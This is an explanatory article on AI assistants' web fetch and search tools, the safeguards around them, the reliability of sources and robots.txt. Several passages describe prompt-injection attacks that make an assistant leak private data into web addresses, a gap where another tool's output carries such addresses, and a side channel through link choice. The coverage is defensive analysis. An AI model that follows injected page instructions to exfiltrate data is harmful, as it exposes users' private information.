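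Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. It then stopped Claude from following links inside fetched pages. dyb points out that this restriction makes it hard for an assistant to work through documentation or other multi-page sites, and suggests letting the assistant follow links only on domains the user has named in the conversation. That seems a reasonable compromise, although it would not protect a user who had named the malicious site.

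The fix seems to apply to the Claude app but not, by default, to the tool for developers. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, the November 2026 Chinese edition of the tool's documentation, still lists earlier fetch results among the accepted sources of links. But developers can now switch off individual sources with the `url_sources` setting, for example to accept links from searches but not from fetched pages. The June edition, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, did not yet include this setting. It warned of "residual risk" and advised worried developers to cap the number of fetches, list allowed domains or disable the tool.

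The November documentation also discloses a more serious gap. A developer's own tool may repeat text that Claude wrote, for example in a program's output or in an error message that quotes a command. If that text contains an address, the fetch tool by default accepts it as coming from a tool result. Claude could then write private data into an address, have the other tool print it, and open it, which the rule is meant to prevent. A developer who also lets Claude run programs should therefore use the new setting to exclude the programs' output.

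Anthropic has also added a check that makes the tool refuse any web address that appears to contain a password or access key, unless that password or key was in the developer's instructions or the text of the user's message. Maria's email address would not trigger this check.

### The rules compared

The guarantees in this table assume that the developer has implemented the rule correctly and applied it everywhere.

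| Rule | What it checks | What it guarantees | What can still leak | What the user loses |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Domain list | The host, ideally at every redirect | No requests to unlisted hosts | Anything that a listed site forwards, stores or counts | Most of the web, if the list is short |
| User approval | Whether the user agrees | No request without consent | Data that the user overlooks or cannot recognize | Time and attention |
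| Anthropic's rule | Whether an accepted source already contained the exact address | The model cannot put data into an address | The choice among supplied links, and addresses that another tool repeats | Guessed or edited addresses and, in the app, links inside fetched pages |
| OpenAI's index rule | Whether a crawler had already found the exact address | No automatic request to an address written for one victim | The choice among indexed pages | Automatic access to new, unlisted and search result pages |
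| Lockdown Mode | Whether OpenAI has a stored copy | No live browsing requests | Data sent through connected apps or Codex | Fresh pages, most images, Deep Research and agent mode |

### When the assistant chooses honestly

ZombieAgent and Paul's attack both depended on the model following an instruction to spell something out. Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) found in *Actions Speak Louder than Words* that a site can also learn from choices the assistant makes for good reasons.

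In their example, a user asks why influenza can be more dangerous than COVID-19 for children. The agent reaches a medical page where the attacker has added a reference link to the attacker's own site. That site offers one page on clinical outcomes and another on biological mechanisms. The agent picks the second, then chooses immune response over pathogenesis. From these choices, the attacker learns roughly what the agent is looking for, although none of the requests contained anything private.

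The researchers first tested how reliably a site can read such choices. They offered the agent four links, only one of which matched what it needed, so its choice could carry two bits. When the agent responded, the researchers identified the matching topic 93.8% of the time. If the errors were spread evenly over the other three links, about 1.6 of the two bits got through. They also tried encoding the choice in the order and the timing of the requests, which worked 67.9% and 58.6% of the time, respectively. Guessing would have been right 25% of the time. The calculated maximum is therefore a fairly good estimate of what a choice of link reveals, but it overstates what an attacker can learn in practice from order or timing.

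The full attack used a series of such choices against four agents with three different models. Liang and colleagues tested it on 500 questions from StackExchange, a group of question-and-answer sites, and 378 turns of conversation from 26 invented users. They scored the results with F1, which is 1 only if the attacker recovers every correct item and no wrong ones. The attack scored 0.89 for the concepts in the users' questions and 0.80 for their personal profiles. It needed only about six choices per question.

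Four existing defenses changed these scores by less than 0.03. They look for hidden instructions, actions that do not fit the task, or sensitive data being sent out. An agent that follows a relevant link shows few of these signs.

The four did not include the address rules of Anthropic or OpenAI. The Claude app should resist this attack fairly well, since it no longer follows links inside fetched pages. The index rule might protect less well, because it checks a page's address but not its content. An attacker could get a few dozen neutral addresses, like `/ref/B1` in the example, into the index and then change the link text for each visitor.

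Liang and colleagues propose that the tool download a fixed number of pages, chosen without regard to the user's private information, and that the agent then pick from the local copies. This reduced both scores to 0.39 without any extra use of the model, although the tool presumably downloads some pages that nobody needs. On the first page of Paul's site, such a tool might fetch all 27 links or a random few, so the server's log would not depend on the user's name.

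## Searching through a search API and filtering the results

Most of the addresses an assistant opens come from a search, so if the search engine or the developer removes a page from the results, the assistant will usually never read it. This filtering happens before the address rules apply, but it only blocks the kinds of page that somebody has chosen to filter out.

### What goes into a search and what comes out

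For the castle question, the model writes a query such as "castle opening hours December Sunday". The developer chooses the other settings in advance. According to Anthropic's *Web search tool*, a guide for developers, these include a list of allowed or blocked domains, a cap on the number of searches and the user's rough location. A made-up result might look like this:

```
url:                https://www.example.com/castle/visit
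title:              Visit the castle
page_age:           November 28, 2026
encrypted_content:  (text from the page, unreadable to the developer)
```

The last field contains the text that Claude reads. The developer's program receives this text only in encrypted form and must return it unchanged with the next message, or the request fails. Anthropic runs the search and gives Claude the results on its own servers, so the developer cannot run a classifier on the text before Claude reads it. To do that, a developer can call a search API from their own program and give Claude only the results that the classifier approves.

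Newer versions of the tool let Claude write code that filters the results before they enter its context. This saves tokens, the word fragments AI companies use to measure and bill text. The code keeps whatever seems relevant, which can include a hostile page about the castle's opening hours, so it is not a safety filter.

A page can drop out at any of these points:

1. The search company's crawler never finds the page, or the site keeps the crawler out.
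2. The search company removes the page as spam or malware, or because of a legal request.
3. SafeSearch excludes it from a particular search.
4. It ranks too low to make the list.
5. The developer's domain list excludes it.
6. The model, or code that the model wrote, discards it.

The model usually cannot tell that a page is missing from the results. In Anthropic's tool, a search that matches nothing returns an empty list instead of an error. A model that can search only three domains might therefore wrongly conclude that the answer isn't on the web.

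### Reading excerpts or opening the page

A model can often answer from the search results alone. *Web search*, OpenAI's guide to its search tool for developers, lists searching, opening a page and finding text in a page as separate actions.

If the assistant answers from excerpts, it does not contact the castle's website. The site's owner therefore cannot learn anything from the requested address or show the assistant a special page, although the site may have shown one to the search engine's crawler earlier. But the excerpt may be out of date or leave out the sentence about the Sunday after Christmas.

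Opening a page gives the assistant its full text, including any hidden instructions, and usually costs more. Anthropic estimates that an average web page uses about 2,500 tokens and a research paper about 125,000. It charges $10 per 1,000 searches plus token costs, but has no separate fee for fetching pages.

When opening a page, the tool may return a stored copy instead of contacting the site. OpenAI's search tool has a setting that allows only stored pages, but the older preview version, which still works, ignores this setting and accesses the live web.

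Amazon's cloud business, AWS, offers a similar tool for the OpenAI models it hosts. According to AWS's *Web Search*, both searching and fetching currently use Amazon's stored copies, even if the developer has permitted live access. A future release may start using that permission, so if a developer grants it now, requests could later leave Amazon's network.

### What the search engine removes

An assistant that uses a search API gets results that the search engine has already ranked and filtered to remove spam and malware. Legal removals also apply, though not always completely. In the EU, for example, people can ask a search engine to stop listing certain pages in searches for their name. Those pages may remain in the index, so an assistant that searches for an event they describe, instead of the person's name, might still find them.

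Search engines also remove pages at different speeds. In July 2026, users found thousands of shared conversations with Claude through Google, some of which reportedly contained cryptocurrency keys. The conversations soon disappeared from Google but stayed visible longer on Bing and Brave, according to The Decoder's *Shared Claude chats were reportedly showing up in search engines*.

Whoever sends a query can usually choose how much SafeSearch filters. Google says its filter covers nudity, explicit content, violence and gore. The table compares Google's filter levels with those of Brave's search API and the Bing API, which Microsoft's *Web Search API v7 query parameters* describes.

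| Search engine | Loosest level | Middle level | Strictest level |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | Off | Blur: obscures explicit images | Filter: removes explicit results |
| Brave API | Off: removes nothing | Moderate (default): removes explicit content | Strict: also removes suggestive content |
| Bing API, now retired | Off: removes adult videos only | Moderate (default): removes adult images and videos, but not adult text | Strict: removes adult text, images and videos |

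Bing's default filter level would have given little protection to a text-based browser like OpenAI's 2023 plugin, because it let adult text through. OpenAI mentioned Microsoft's "safe-mode" but not the level it used. The level names are misleading for a developer who changes supplier, because Brave's "moderate" level filters explicit text and Bing's did not.

Google acknowledges in *Fix problems with SafeSearch* that no filter is completely accurate. It also deliberately leaves in explicit material of significant artistic, educational, historical, documentary or scientific value, a policy that suits historical research better than use in a primary school.

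None of the three companies seems to have published an error rate for its filter. A developer can run the same queries at two filter levels and compare the results to see what the stricter level removed. Someone has to check the remaining pages to find what it missed.

SafeSearch is designed to filter out sex and violence, not falsehoods, scams or hidden instructions. It may therefore let through a page with the wrong opening hours, a fake ticket shop or a page with an instruction hidden in white text. Spam and malware removal might catch the ticket shop but is less likely to catch the hidden instruction, because search companies developed these systems mainly to protect human visitors, whom the instruction does not affect.

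SafeSearch also has no effect outside the search results. Google notes that it does not affect websites a person visits directly, and the same applies when an assistant opens a harmless result and then follows a link to an explicit page.

### Domain lists in search tools

A domain list in a search tool filters the results, but it does not stop a separate fetch tool from opening an excluded page if the address came from somewhere else. The developer has to set a list for each tool, and the two tools may interpret the same entry differently. For example, Anthropic's search tool, unlike its fetch tool, can match an entry that includes a path.

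| Entry in both tools | Search tool | Fetch tool |
|---|---|---|
| Allow only `example.com/blog` | Returns pages from the blog | Refuses to open them |
| Block `example.com/forum` | Leaves out pages from the forum | Can still open them |

Testing the assistant reveals the first mistake immediately, but the second could go unnoticed because the forum does disappear from the search results.

OpenAI's tool accepts up to 100 allowed or 100 blocked domains. A list of 100 allowed domains is plenty for an assistant that should search only medical journals and health agencies. A blocklist can exclude a few known nuisances, but it offers little protection against scammers, who can keep registering new domains. OpenAI's older preview tool and its specialized search models do not support domain lists.

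Look-alike letters are a problem in search tools too. Browsers and servers convert a domain with non-Latin letters into a plain-letter form before looking it up. For example, `amazon.com` with a Cyrillic "а" becomes `xn--mazon-3ve.com`, so a developer who converts every entry in a domain list before saving it will see the difference. In June 2026 Anthropic advised developers to use only plain letters where possible and to test their lists with look-alikes. It also warned that programs may process such letters differently, so two parts of the same system could get different results when checking whether an address is on the list.

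An organization can also set a list for all its developers. An individual request to Anthropic's tool can narrow that list but not extend it, so one carelessly configured project can't gain access to the whole web.

### What the search company learns

When an assistant searches through an outside company, that company receives the queries. ChatGPT usually rewrites the user's question first, sometimes with details from its memory of earlier conversations. OpenAI's *Searching the web with ChatGPT* gives the example of a user who has mentioned being vegan and living in San Francisco. If this user asks for nearby restaurants, ChatGPT may search for "good vegan restaurants San Francisco". The search company receives a detail about the user's diet that was not in the question.

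OpenAI does not send search companies the user's IP address or account information, although it may send a rough location. For business and university customers, it may send queries to Bing without any account, device or session identifier, according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT search for Enterprise and Edu*. Microsoft's privacy policy then applies to those queries.

Removing the identifiers makes it harder to link a query to a person, but the words in the query may still identify the person. A search for a rare illness in a small town may point to one patient, and a search for two company names and "merger" may reveal a confidential plan. ChatGPT for Healthcare avoids part of this problem by not using Bing.

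Some organizations can instead limit ChatGPT to OpenAI's own index and stored pages without the other restrictions of Lockdown Mode. According to OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces*, this reduces the chance that a query reaches an outside search company, but some pages may be missing or incomplete. OpenAI does not promise to refresh any particular page by a set date, and the results may not show when OpenAI stored a page. Offline search is therefore a poor way to prove what a page contained on a given day.

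The developer also depends on a ranking it cannot inspect. OpenAI says it uses "multiple factors" to help users find relevant, reliable information. Its tool for developers can return every address the model consulted, often more than the model cites. The list helps a developer trace a wrong answer to its source, but it does not show why a better page ranked lower or never appeared.

### After the Bing APIs

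The Bing search API that OpenAI used in 2023 no longer exists. On May 12, 2025, Microsoft gave developers three months' notice that it would shut down the Bing Search APIs, as PPC Land's *Microsoft ends Bing Search APIs on August 11* (2025) reported. Larger customers such as the search engine DuckDuckGo would reportedly keep their access, according to Thurrott's *Microsoft is Retiring Bing Search APIs* (2025).

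Microsoft's *Bing Search API retirement* directed other customers to Grounding with Bing Search, which supplies web data to AI agents on Microsoft's cloud. PPC Land put the price increase at 40% to 483%. The old API returned a list of results that a developer could filter and give to any model. The replacement is part of Microsoft's agent service, so developers presumably have less freedom to do either.

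OpenAI had already stopped relying on a single supplier when it launched ChatGPT search in 2024. The product used several outside search providers and content supplied directly by partners, according to OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT search*. OpenAI now also has its own index.

Peec AI's *ChatGPT search result providers*, a September 2026 study by an analytics company, identified at least eight outside sources in addition to that index. The researchers relied on technical data from ChatGPT's servers and on public confirmations, and concluded that some of these sources copy Google's results pages automatically. If so, part of what ChatGPT finds reflects Google's ranking and removals, even though OpenAI does not get those results directly from Google.

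OpenAI now has good reason to invest in its own index. In November 2026 it said that the number of ChatGPT queries that trigger a web search equalled 20% of Google's search volume, according to UA.News' *OpenAI says ChatGPT web search has reached 20% of Google’s volume*. OpenAI did not explain where it got the Google figure. Bing had about 3% of the search market in 2023, by its chief executive's estimate.

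Anthropic has disclosed less about its search supplier. In March 2025 it added Brave Search to its list of outside companies that process data for it. The same week, Simon Willison asked Claude a question and found that the ten sources it cited exactly matched Brave's results. In November 2026, Search Engine Journal could not confirm whether Claude still uses Brave (*Brave Sells Its Search Index To AI*). Anthropic also has its own crawler, Claude-SearchBot, which indexes pages for search, according to Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic’s Claude Bots Make Robots.txt Decisions More Granular*.

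Brave has an index of more than 30 billion pages and names Cohere, Mistral, Perplexity and You.com among the customers of its search API. On November 2, 2026, the New York Times sued Brave for copying its articles and selling access to them. IBTimes UK's *New York Times Lawsuit Accuses Brave Browser of Scraping Paywalled Journalism* reports that the newspaper wants the court to stop Brave from distributing its work. If the newspaper wins, every assistant that uses Brave's API could lose access to those articles.

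### Who filters the results now

| Product | Where results come from | Who filters them first |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT's 2023 browsing plugin | Bing | Microsoft |
| ChatGPT in 2026 | OpenAI's index and outside providers | OpenAI for its own index, each provider for the rest |
| Claude | Brave in 2025, current mix not public | Not public |
| OpenAI models on Amazon's cloud | Amazon's index | Amazon |
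| AI agents that use Microsoft's replacement service | Bing | Microsoft |

Filtering depends on both the model and where a customer buys it. GPT-5.6 Sol searches Amazon's index on Amazon's cloud, but not when a developer buys it from OpenAI. A company that tested its assistant on one platform should repeat the search tests if it moves to the other.

A company that builds its own index has to do the work that OpenAI once left to Microsoft. It has to find spam and malware, process legal requests and decide how to treat explicit pages. It also has to delete its stored copies when a page is taken down, or the assistant may keep quoting text the owner has withdrawn.

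A company with its own index can also check pages for hidden instructions before any assistant reads them. The small detector described earlier costs $0.18 per 1,000 pages, so one pass over 30 billion pages would cost about $5.4 million. A large AI company could afford that, but the detector had a 7% false alarm rate in testing, and at that rate it could wrongly flag up to about 2 billion clean pages. The check would also miss instructions that a site hides from the crawler or adds later.

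Developers have lost the SafeSearch setting they had with Bing. Anthropic's search tool doesn't have one, and OpenAI's apparently doesn't either. Someone who builds a homework assistant for children on either tool can't request strict filtering. They have to rely on what the company already removes, limit searches to a list of suitable sites, or check the answer before a child sees it.

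## How reliable the retrieved sources are

A page can pass a search engine's filters and still be wrong. Nakano and colleagues noticed that WebGPT sometimes quoted highly unreliable pages despite Bing's filtering. This happened on TruthfulQA, a set of questions that invite common misconceptions. When asked whether someone who dreams of doing something and makes a wish will succeed, WebGPT answered that the power of thought can make a wish come true.

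The researchers trained WebGPT mostly on ordinary questions from Reddit and suspected that the trick questions in TruthfulQA were too different from these. Its answers to TruthfulQA were still true 75% of the time, which was better than GPT-3 without a browser. But the scoring counted evasive answers as true, and only 54% of WebGPT's answers were both true and informative.

Nakano and colleagues also worried that their training could reward a model for picking references that people found convincing, even if these did not reflect the evidence fairly, because people judged the answers partly by their references. WebGPT already showed early signs of this, because it usually accepted whatever a question assumed. The researchers expected the problem to get worse with more capable models, and suggested training models to find evidence both for and against a claim.

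An answer with citations therefore raises three separate questions:

- Is the source trustworthy? A travel blog may list the castle's opening hours from five years ago.
- Does the answer state what the source says? The castle's own page may say that it closes on Sundays in winter, and the assistant may leave out "in winter".
- Did the assistant choose its sources fairly? If the user asks whether the castle is worth a visit, the assistant might cite three glowing reviews and skip the critical ones.

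A user who opens a citation can check whether the answer matches the page. This check may not show whether the page is correct, and it doesn't show anything about the pages the assistant left out.

### Signals of a trustworthy page

A program can't see directly whether a page is true, so search engines and assistants have to rely on indirect signals.

| Signal | What it can show | Where it misleads |
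|---|---|---|
| Links from other sites | Other authors thought the page worth pointing to | New pages have few links, and site owners can buy them |
| The site's reputation | The publisher has been reliable before | A reputable site may also carry satire, advertising or readers' posts |
| Human quality ratings | Trained raters found similar results useful and reliable | Raters see only a small sample and often disagree |
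| Publisher ratings | The publisher meets certain standards, such as correcting its errors | They mostly cover news, and they apply to a whole publisher |
| Agreement between sources | Several authors reached the same conclusion | They may all have copied the same page |

These methods all depend on someone having already looked at the page, its publisher or its subject, so they are weakest for small sites and breaking news. Careful raters also disagree. Even with detailed instructions, WebGPT's raters agreed on which of two answers was better only 73% of the time.

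### How models weigh conflicting sources

Search companies built their rankings for people who look at a list of results. A person may recognize some of the sites, skip any that look odd and compare two pages, so one good result among ten can be enough. An assistant merges a few of the results into one answer, and the user may never see the rest. The ranking also favors pages that match the query, and a page that repeats a false assumption in the question may match better than one that corrects it.

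In *Synthetic Web*, Shah and Ozgur (2026) measured how badly a single false search result can mislead a model. They generated four fictional miniature webs, with 15,476 articles on 77 sites, so that models could not answer from memory. Six OpenAI models answered 587 questions, ten times each under two conditions. The search tool returned ordinary results in one condition, and in the other it put a false article, written for that question, at the top of the first list of results.

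With the false article present, GPT-5's accuracy fell from 65.1% to 18.2%, and that of the older o3 fell from 48.4% to 16.7%. The articles with the correct information were still available, and the models could use their tools for up to 100 rounds. But GPT-5 made about as many tool calls with the false article (6.61 on average) as without it (6.45), and the models' confidence in their wrong answers stayed high. People who used the same search tool answered 98% of questions correctly without the false article and 93% with it, although this was a small sample from one of the four webs.

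The experiment does not show how much of this large drop came from the ranking, because the researchers never placed the same article lower in the list, where its invented studies and figures might have been almost as persuasive. On the real web, a model can compare a claim with what it learned in training, and a commercial assistant may have checks that these models lacked.

Figures can be persuasive even when they are impossible. Pradhan and Goley (2026), in *Trust, but Don't Verify*, showed six models a workplace chat in which four sources gave estimates, and then asked for the model's own estimate. In the main comparison, one source disagreed with the rest. The researchers measured its influence like this:

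`influence = (model's estimate − average of the others) / (lone source's estimate − average of the others)`

If the other sources average 82% and the lone source gives 49%, a model's answer of 60% means the lone source has an influence score of 0.67. The score is 0 when the answer matches the others' average and 1 when it matches the lone source.

In some versions, the lone source contained impossible statistics, such as a margin of error at least 50 times too small for the number of customers studied. The source's influence on Claude Opus 4.5 was 0.67 with impossible statistics and 0.68 with valid ones. When the researchers showed the model only the claim about customers and asked for a review, it identified the flaw every time.

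Pradhan and Goley conclude that models can detect such flaws but fail to do so when they combine sources. This conclusion fits two of the three topics better than the third, where the flaw was so technical that most models rarely identified it even in a separate review. The test also used a chat, so results might differ with web pages.

For most models, an instruction to check the statistics reduced the influence of valid figures as well as impossible ones. In GPT-5.4, the influence of impossible statistics fell by 0.19 and that of valid ones by 0.15. The researchers call this blanket skepticism. Opus 4.5 did noticeably better with the same instruction, which lowered the influence of impossible statistics to 0.43 but that of valid ones only to 0.63.

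A publisher's name can also affect which text a model selects. Khan, Amani and colleagues (*In Agents We Trust, but Who Do Agents Trust?*, 2026) gave twelve models pairs of news stories with the same meaning but different outlet names, and asked which story had higher journalistic standards. The larger models strongly favored some outlets, and models from different companies tended to favor the same ones. Telling the models to ignore the source had little effect.

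Models' reliance on source names is partly sensible. When choosing between research papers, they picked one labelled as from the New England Journal of Medicine 96% of the time if the topic was health, but only 19% of the time if it was computer vision. However, names are easy to imitate. The models treated an outlet's name, website and social media accounts similarly if they looked alike, so a fake site with a similar name might benefit from the real outlet's reputation.

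### Tests of commercial assistants

NewsGuard, a company that rates news publishers, regularly asks leading chatbots about false claims spreading online. *AI False Information Rate Nearly Doubles in One Year* (2025) compares NewsGuard's audits from August 2024 and August 2025. In the table, the share of corrected claims is 100% minus the other two shares.

| Response to a false claim | August 2024 | August 2025 |
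|---|---|---|
| Repeated it | 18% | 35% |
| Did not answer | 31% | 0% |
| Corrected it | 51% | 65% |

The chatbots thus repeated more false claims but also corrected more. When they answered, they repeated the false claim 26% of the time in 2024 and 35% in 2025. The chatbots' no longer declining to answer therefore explains about half of the increase in repeated claims, assuming that the questions they had declined were no harder than the rest.

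NewsGuard blames web search, which led the chatbots to unreliable sites. That is plausible, but the chatbots gained web access and stopped declining questions over the same period, so the audit cannot separate the effects of the two changes. Axios' *Popular chatbots amplify misinformation* (2025) notes that both also made the chatbots more useful and accurate for some questions.

The audits cover only provably false claims, so a 35% failure rate does not mean that a third of ordinary answers are false. The scores for individual chatbots are also imprecise. According to The Decoder, Mistral's chatbot repeated false claims 36.67% of the time in both years, which corresponds to 11 answers out of 30. With so few answers, the true rate could easily be 15 percentage points higher or lower. According to a NewsGuard press release (2025), the company supplies data for improving AI models, so it also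 has a commercial interest in the results.

Later results look somewhat better. NewsGuard's *Quarterly AI False Claim Monitor* (2026) put the average for eleven chatbots in January 2026 at just over 28%. In July, NewsGuard and the US broadcaster NPR asked six chatbots 30 questions about false stories spread by Russia, China and Iran. NPR's *We tested how AI chatbots would handle foreign propaganda* (2026) reports that the chatbots clearly corrected the stories about three-quarters of the time. The tests used different questions, so these figures do not establish a trend.

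NPR also ran the questions through four search engines, which few audits do. A page of search results failed if all its relevant links repeated the false story, and a chatbot failed if it did not challenge the story at all. By this lenient standard, the chatbots failed less often than the search engines. The AI summaries above search results failed more often than the links below them. Google's summaries corrected most of the false stories, but Bing's did not.

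The European Broadcasting Union (EBU) and the BBC organized the largest manual check of whether AI assistants' answers about news match their sources. In May and June 2025, 22 public broadcasters from 18 countries put 30 questions to the free versions of ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity. Journalists then assessed 2,709 answers in 14 languages.

EBU's *News Integrity in AI Assistants* (2025) reports that 45% of AI assistants' answers about news had at least one significant problem. The most common was sourcing, which affected 31% of answers and included claims that the cited page did not support and answers without any source. Accuracy was a significant problem in 20% of answers, and missing context in 14%.

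Gemini greatly raised the overall rate of sourcing problems, with significant ones in 72% of its answers compared with an average of about 18% for the other three assistants. The journalists had a stake in the outcome because they worked for organizations that want more control over how AI companies use their reporting. Each question asked the assistant to use the broadcaster's own reporting where possible, which most users would not do. On the BBC's questions, the share of answers with significant problems fell from 51% in an earlier round to 37%.

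In one answer about whether Elon Musk had given a Nazi salute, Gemini quoted a satirical Radio France program as if it were news. It also altered the quotation and linked it to an unrelated video from a British newspaper.

Chatbots now seem to make more errors by failing to find the right page than by misreading it. Stanford HAI's *Reading Today's Headlines Through AI* (2026) describes a February 2026 test in which six chatbots each answered 2,100 multiple-choice questions, in six languages, about BBC stories published the same day. About 12% of the 12,600 answers were wrong. In 38.8% of these errors, the chatbot had not found a sufficiently relevant page, and in another 32.7% it had used a page on the same subject with different facts. When a chatbot did find a correct source, it almost always answered correctly.

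The chatbots' average score was 79.3% in Hindi and 88.9% to 91.3% in the other languages. They understood Hindi well but often relied on English pages. For example, a BBC Hindi article gave India's share of the world's merchant sailors as 7%, but a chatbot answered 10%, an estimate it had found on an English industry site. Accuracy also fell by 16 to 17 percentage points when the researchers removed the answer options, so accuracy in everyday use is probably lower than the multiple-choice scores.

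### Pages written for machines

NewsGuard describes networks of websites with few human visitors, some of them part of Russian influence campaigns, that publish falsehoods where AI systems will find them. One is the pro-Kremlin Pravda network. The Decoder reported that Microsoft's Copilot stopped quoting the network's sites in March 2025 but then began to cite its posts on VK, a Russian social media platform. A blocklist of the network's domains would not have blocked those posts.

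Publishing the same claim on many sites can sway models because they respond to repetition. *Whose Facts Win?* (Schuster, Gautam and Markert, 2026) gave 13 open models tables with conflicting facts about fictional people and places. The models generally preferred government sources to newspapers, and both to individuals and social media accounts. The researchers then had a social media account contradict a government agency and varied how often the account's version appeared.

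| How the social media version appeared | Average shift towards it |
|---|---|
| Twice, from two different accounts | 34 points |
| Twice, from the same account | 30 points |
| Once, with two accounts named as its sources | 6 points |

Seeing the text twice therefore affected the models much more than learning that a second account agreed. Someone who runs a network of sites may only need to copy one article across them to sway a model. However, the models had to choose an answer without reasoning first, and a model that can think or search further might notice the duplication.

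AI assistants are most likely to repeat false stories when few reliable pages cover the same subject. NewsGuard (2025) observed in its June 2025 audit that reliable reports about breaking news often appeared later than the false claims, or were scarce. NPR describes a working paper by Morgan Wack, a researcher at the University of Zurich, and colleagues, which found that AI tools gave inaccurate information more often when questionable sources were plentiful and reliable ones were scarce. Obscure subjects may never attract enough reliable pages to correct this imbalance.

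A business can also optimize its pages for assistants without publishing anything false, much as it would for a search engine. Pradhan and Goley's results suggest that adding a description of a method and precise figures would help, even if the figures make no sense. *Retrieval Collapses When AI Pollutes the Web* (2026) examined what happens when AI generates many such pages. Pages optimized for search reduced the variety of sources while answers remained accurate, so a test of accuracy alone would have missed the change. With deliberately false pages, exposure reached 19% under BM25, a standard method that ranks pages by matching words. Rankers based on language models reduced this exposure but needed much more computing power. The researchers have yet to confirm these results on the live web.

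Tests of real products suggest that state propaganda is less of a danger than some of these experiments imply. In NPR's test, chatbots cited state-controlled and state-aligned media about as often as search engines linked to them, but were better at challenging false stories. *Wrong on Sunday, right on Monday* describes a project in which the British fact-checking charity Full Fact put 22 questions to leading chatbots every day for ten weeks. None of the chatbots repeated the core misinformation around some of the more sensitive political questions. More common failures included presenting an old policy as current and giving rules from one part of the UK as if they applied everywhere.

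NPR's result may not hold for newer stories, because some of the false stories in the test had circulated for months and fact-checkers had time to respond. The test was also entirely in English. NPR cites a study in *Nature* in which models gave more positive answers about China's government when researchers asked in Chinese.

### What the remedies cost

An assistant could favor publishers with good ratings. NewsGuard says it has data on more than 35,000 sources and that its ratings cover 95% of people's online engagement with news in nine countries. That may be enough for an assistant that answers questions about American politics, but the castle's website probably has no rating, and neither do most local clubs, small companies and personal blogs. A rule that allowed only well-rated publishers would exclude them all. It would also have let through the satire from Radio France, because the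 ratings apply to whole publishers.

Ratings are not neutral, because somebody has to decide what counts as reliable, but Khan and colleagues showed that leaving the choice to the model is not neutral either. A published list at least lets users and publishers see the standards and object to them.

Asking the model itself to rate the sources has so far achieved little. In a small experiment in *ConflictScore* (2026), the open model gpt-oss-20b assessed how trustworthy its documents were before rewriting its answers to TruthfulQA, and its score rose from 85.03 to 85.19.

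AI companies also sign commercial licensing agreements with publishers, which give an assistant dependable access to professional reporting but do not certify its accuracy. If an assistant favors licensed publishers, smaller publishers without a deal may lose readers. They may even be missing from the retrieved sources altogether, especially since reputable sites block AI visitors more often than less reputable ones do.

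All the questions in Stanford HAI's test came from BBC stories, but Claude Sonnet 4.5 never cited the BBC and GPT-5 cited it in only 0.2% of its answers. Grok 4 cited it in 28.5%, although it has no publicly known agreement with the BBC. The BBC restricts AI companies' access to its site and has threatened some with legal action. The researchers think the difference mostly reflects which companies respect those restrictions, so a test like this can penalize an assistant for following a publisher's wishes.

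Showing citations barely reduces coverage, but it only helps if the cited pages support the answer and somebody reads them. NPR cites a Washington University in St. Louis study which found that about one in nine factual claims in Google's AI summaries lacked support from the cited sources. Most of these claims had no citation, and a small fraction were fabricated.

In the Digital News Report 2026, a large international survey, 4% of all respondents said they always or often click through from chatbots to the original sources, compared with 19% for search engines, according to The Decoder's *More people get news from AI chatbots, but trust remains low*. Press Gazette gives a figure of 42% from the same survey, which covers only people who use chatbots for news. The two figures are consistent, because about 10% of respondents use chatbots for news each week, and 42% of 10% is roughly 4%.

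A substantial minority of these users say they often check the sources. The survey relies on self-reports, so people may click less often than they say. Researchers and journalists can still use the links to audit an assistant on everyone else's behalf.

A developer could require several independent sources before the assistant states something as fact. This would have helped in Shah and Ozgur's experiment, where several articles supported the correct answer and usually only one supported the false claim. However, the assistant would have to open more pages, which takes more time and money, and each page may contain hidden instructions. The requirement also fails for facts that only one source can supply. For example, a castle's website may be the only place that lists its current holiday hours, and ten travel sites that copied last year's hours would outnumber it.

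Software can count domains more easily than it can determine whether they are independent. It could merge near-identical texts before the model reads them, but a network of sites can avoid this by using AI to reword each copy. Schuster and colleagues trained a small model, Gemma 3 4B, to give the same answer whether or not a text was repeated. Combined with an instruction to consider credibility, this training reduced the effect of repetition by up to 79.2% and kept at least 72.5% of the model's original preference between sources. They tested it only on the same kind of fictional tables, so it may work less well on web pages.

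Declining to answer prevents false answers but also loses correct ones. Between NewsGuard's two audits, the share of unanswered questions fell by 31 percentage points, while correct answers rose by 14 points and false ones by 17. The audits did not test the same claims, so this is only a rough estimate of the tradeoff. Given this tradeoff, declining seems worthwhile for a question about a medicine, where a false answer could do serious harm, but less so for one about a film. Assistants now rarely decline questions about news. In the EBU study, they declined 17 of 3,113 questions, or about 0.5%.

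An assistant can also answer and say how uncertain it is, which preserves more of the useful information. But it may flag a problem and still answer incorrectly. When Stanford HAI researchers added one false detail to each question, Gemini 3 Pro flagged 80% of them but answered only 55% of the questions correctly.

The placement of a warning matters too. In NPR's test, Meta AI treated an invented report about Ukrainian soldiers in France as real and did not mention until the sixth paragraph that it had found no official confirmation. It could have put that sentence first without leaving anything out, although people would probably start to skip such warnings if every answer began with one.

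## What robots.txt says and which assistants follow it

Some reliable pages are missing from assistants' answers because their owners do not want AI companies to fetch them. Owners usually state this in a robots.txt file, a format Martijn Koster devised in 1994 to tell crawlers where they could go on a site. Developers followed it by custom until 2022, when Koster published a formal standard, *Robots Exclusion Protocol* (RFC 9309), with Illyes and two other Google employees.

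### How a program reads the file

The file is always at the same place on a site, for example `https://www.example.com/robots.txt`, and its rules cover only that host. A shop at `shop.example.com` needs its own file. A program that follows the standard does this before it requests a page:

1. It downloads the file, or uses a copy that is normally no more than 24 hours old.
2. It looks for a group that contains its name. A group consists of one or more `User-agent` lines and the rules below them. If several groups name the program, it combines their rules.
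3. If no group names it, it uses the group for `*`, which stands for everyone else. If there is no such group either, it may request anything.
4. It compares the address, from the first slash after the host, with every `Allow` and `Disallow` rule in its group.
5. It obeys the longest rule that matches. `Allow` wins a tie, and if nothing matches, the program may request the page.

The order of the rules makes no difference. Capital letters do not matter in the program's name, but they do in the path.

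Step 3 causes a common misunderstanding. Suppose the castle's owner wants to keep all automated visitors out, except that Claude-User may open the page with the opening hours:

```
User-agent: *
Disallow: /

User-agent: Claude-User
Allow: /castle/visit
```

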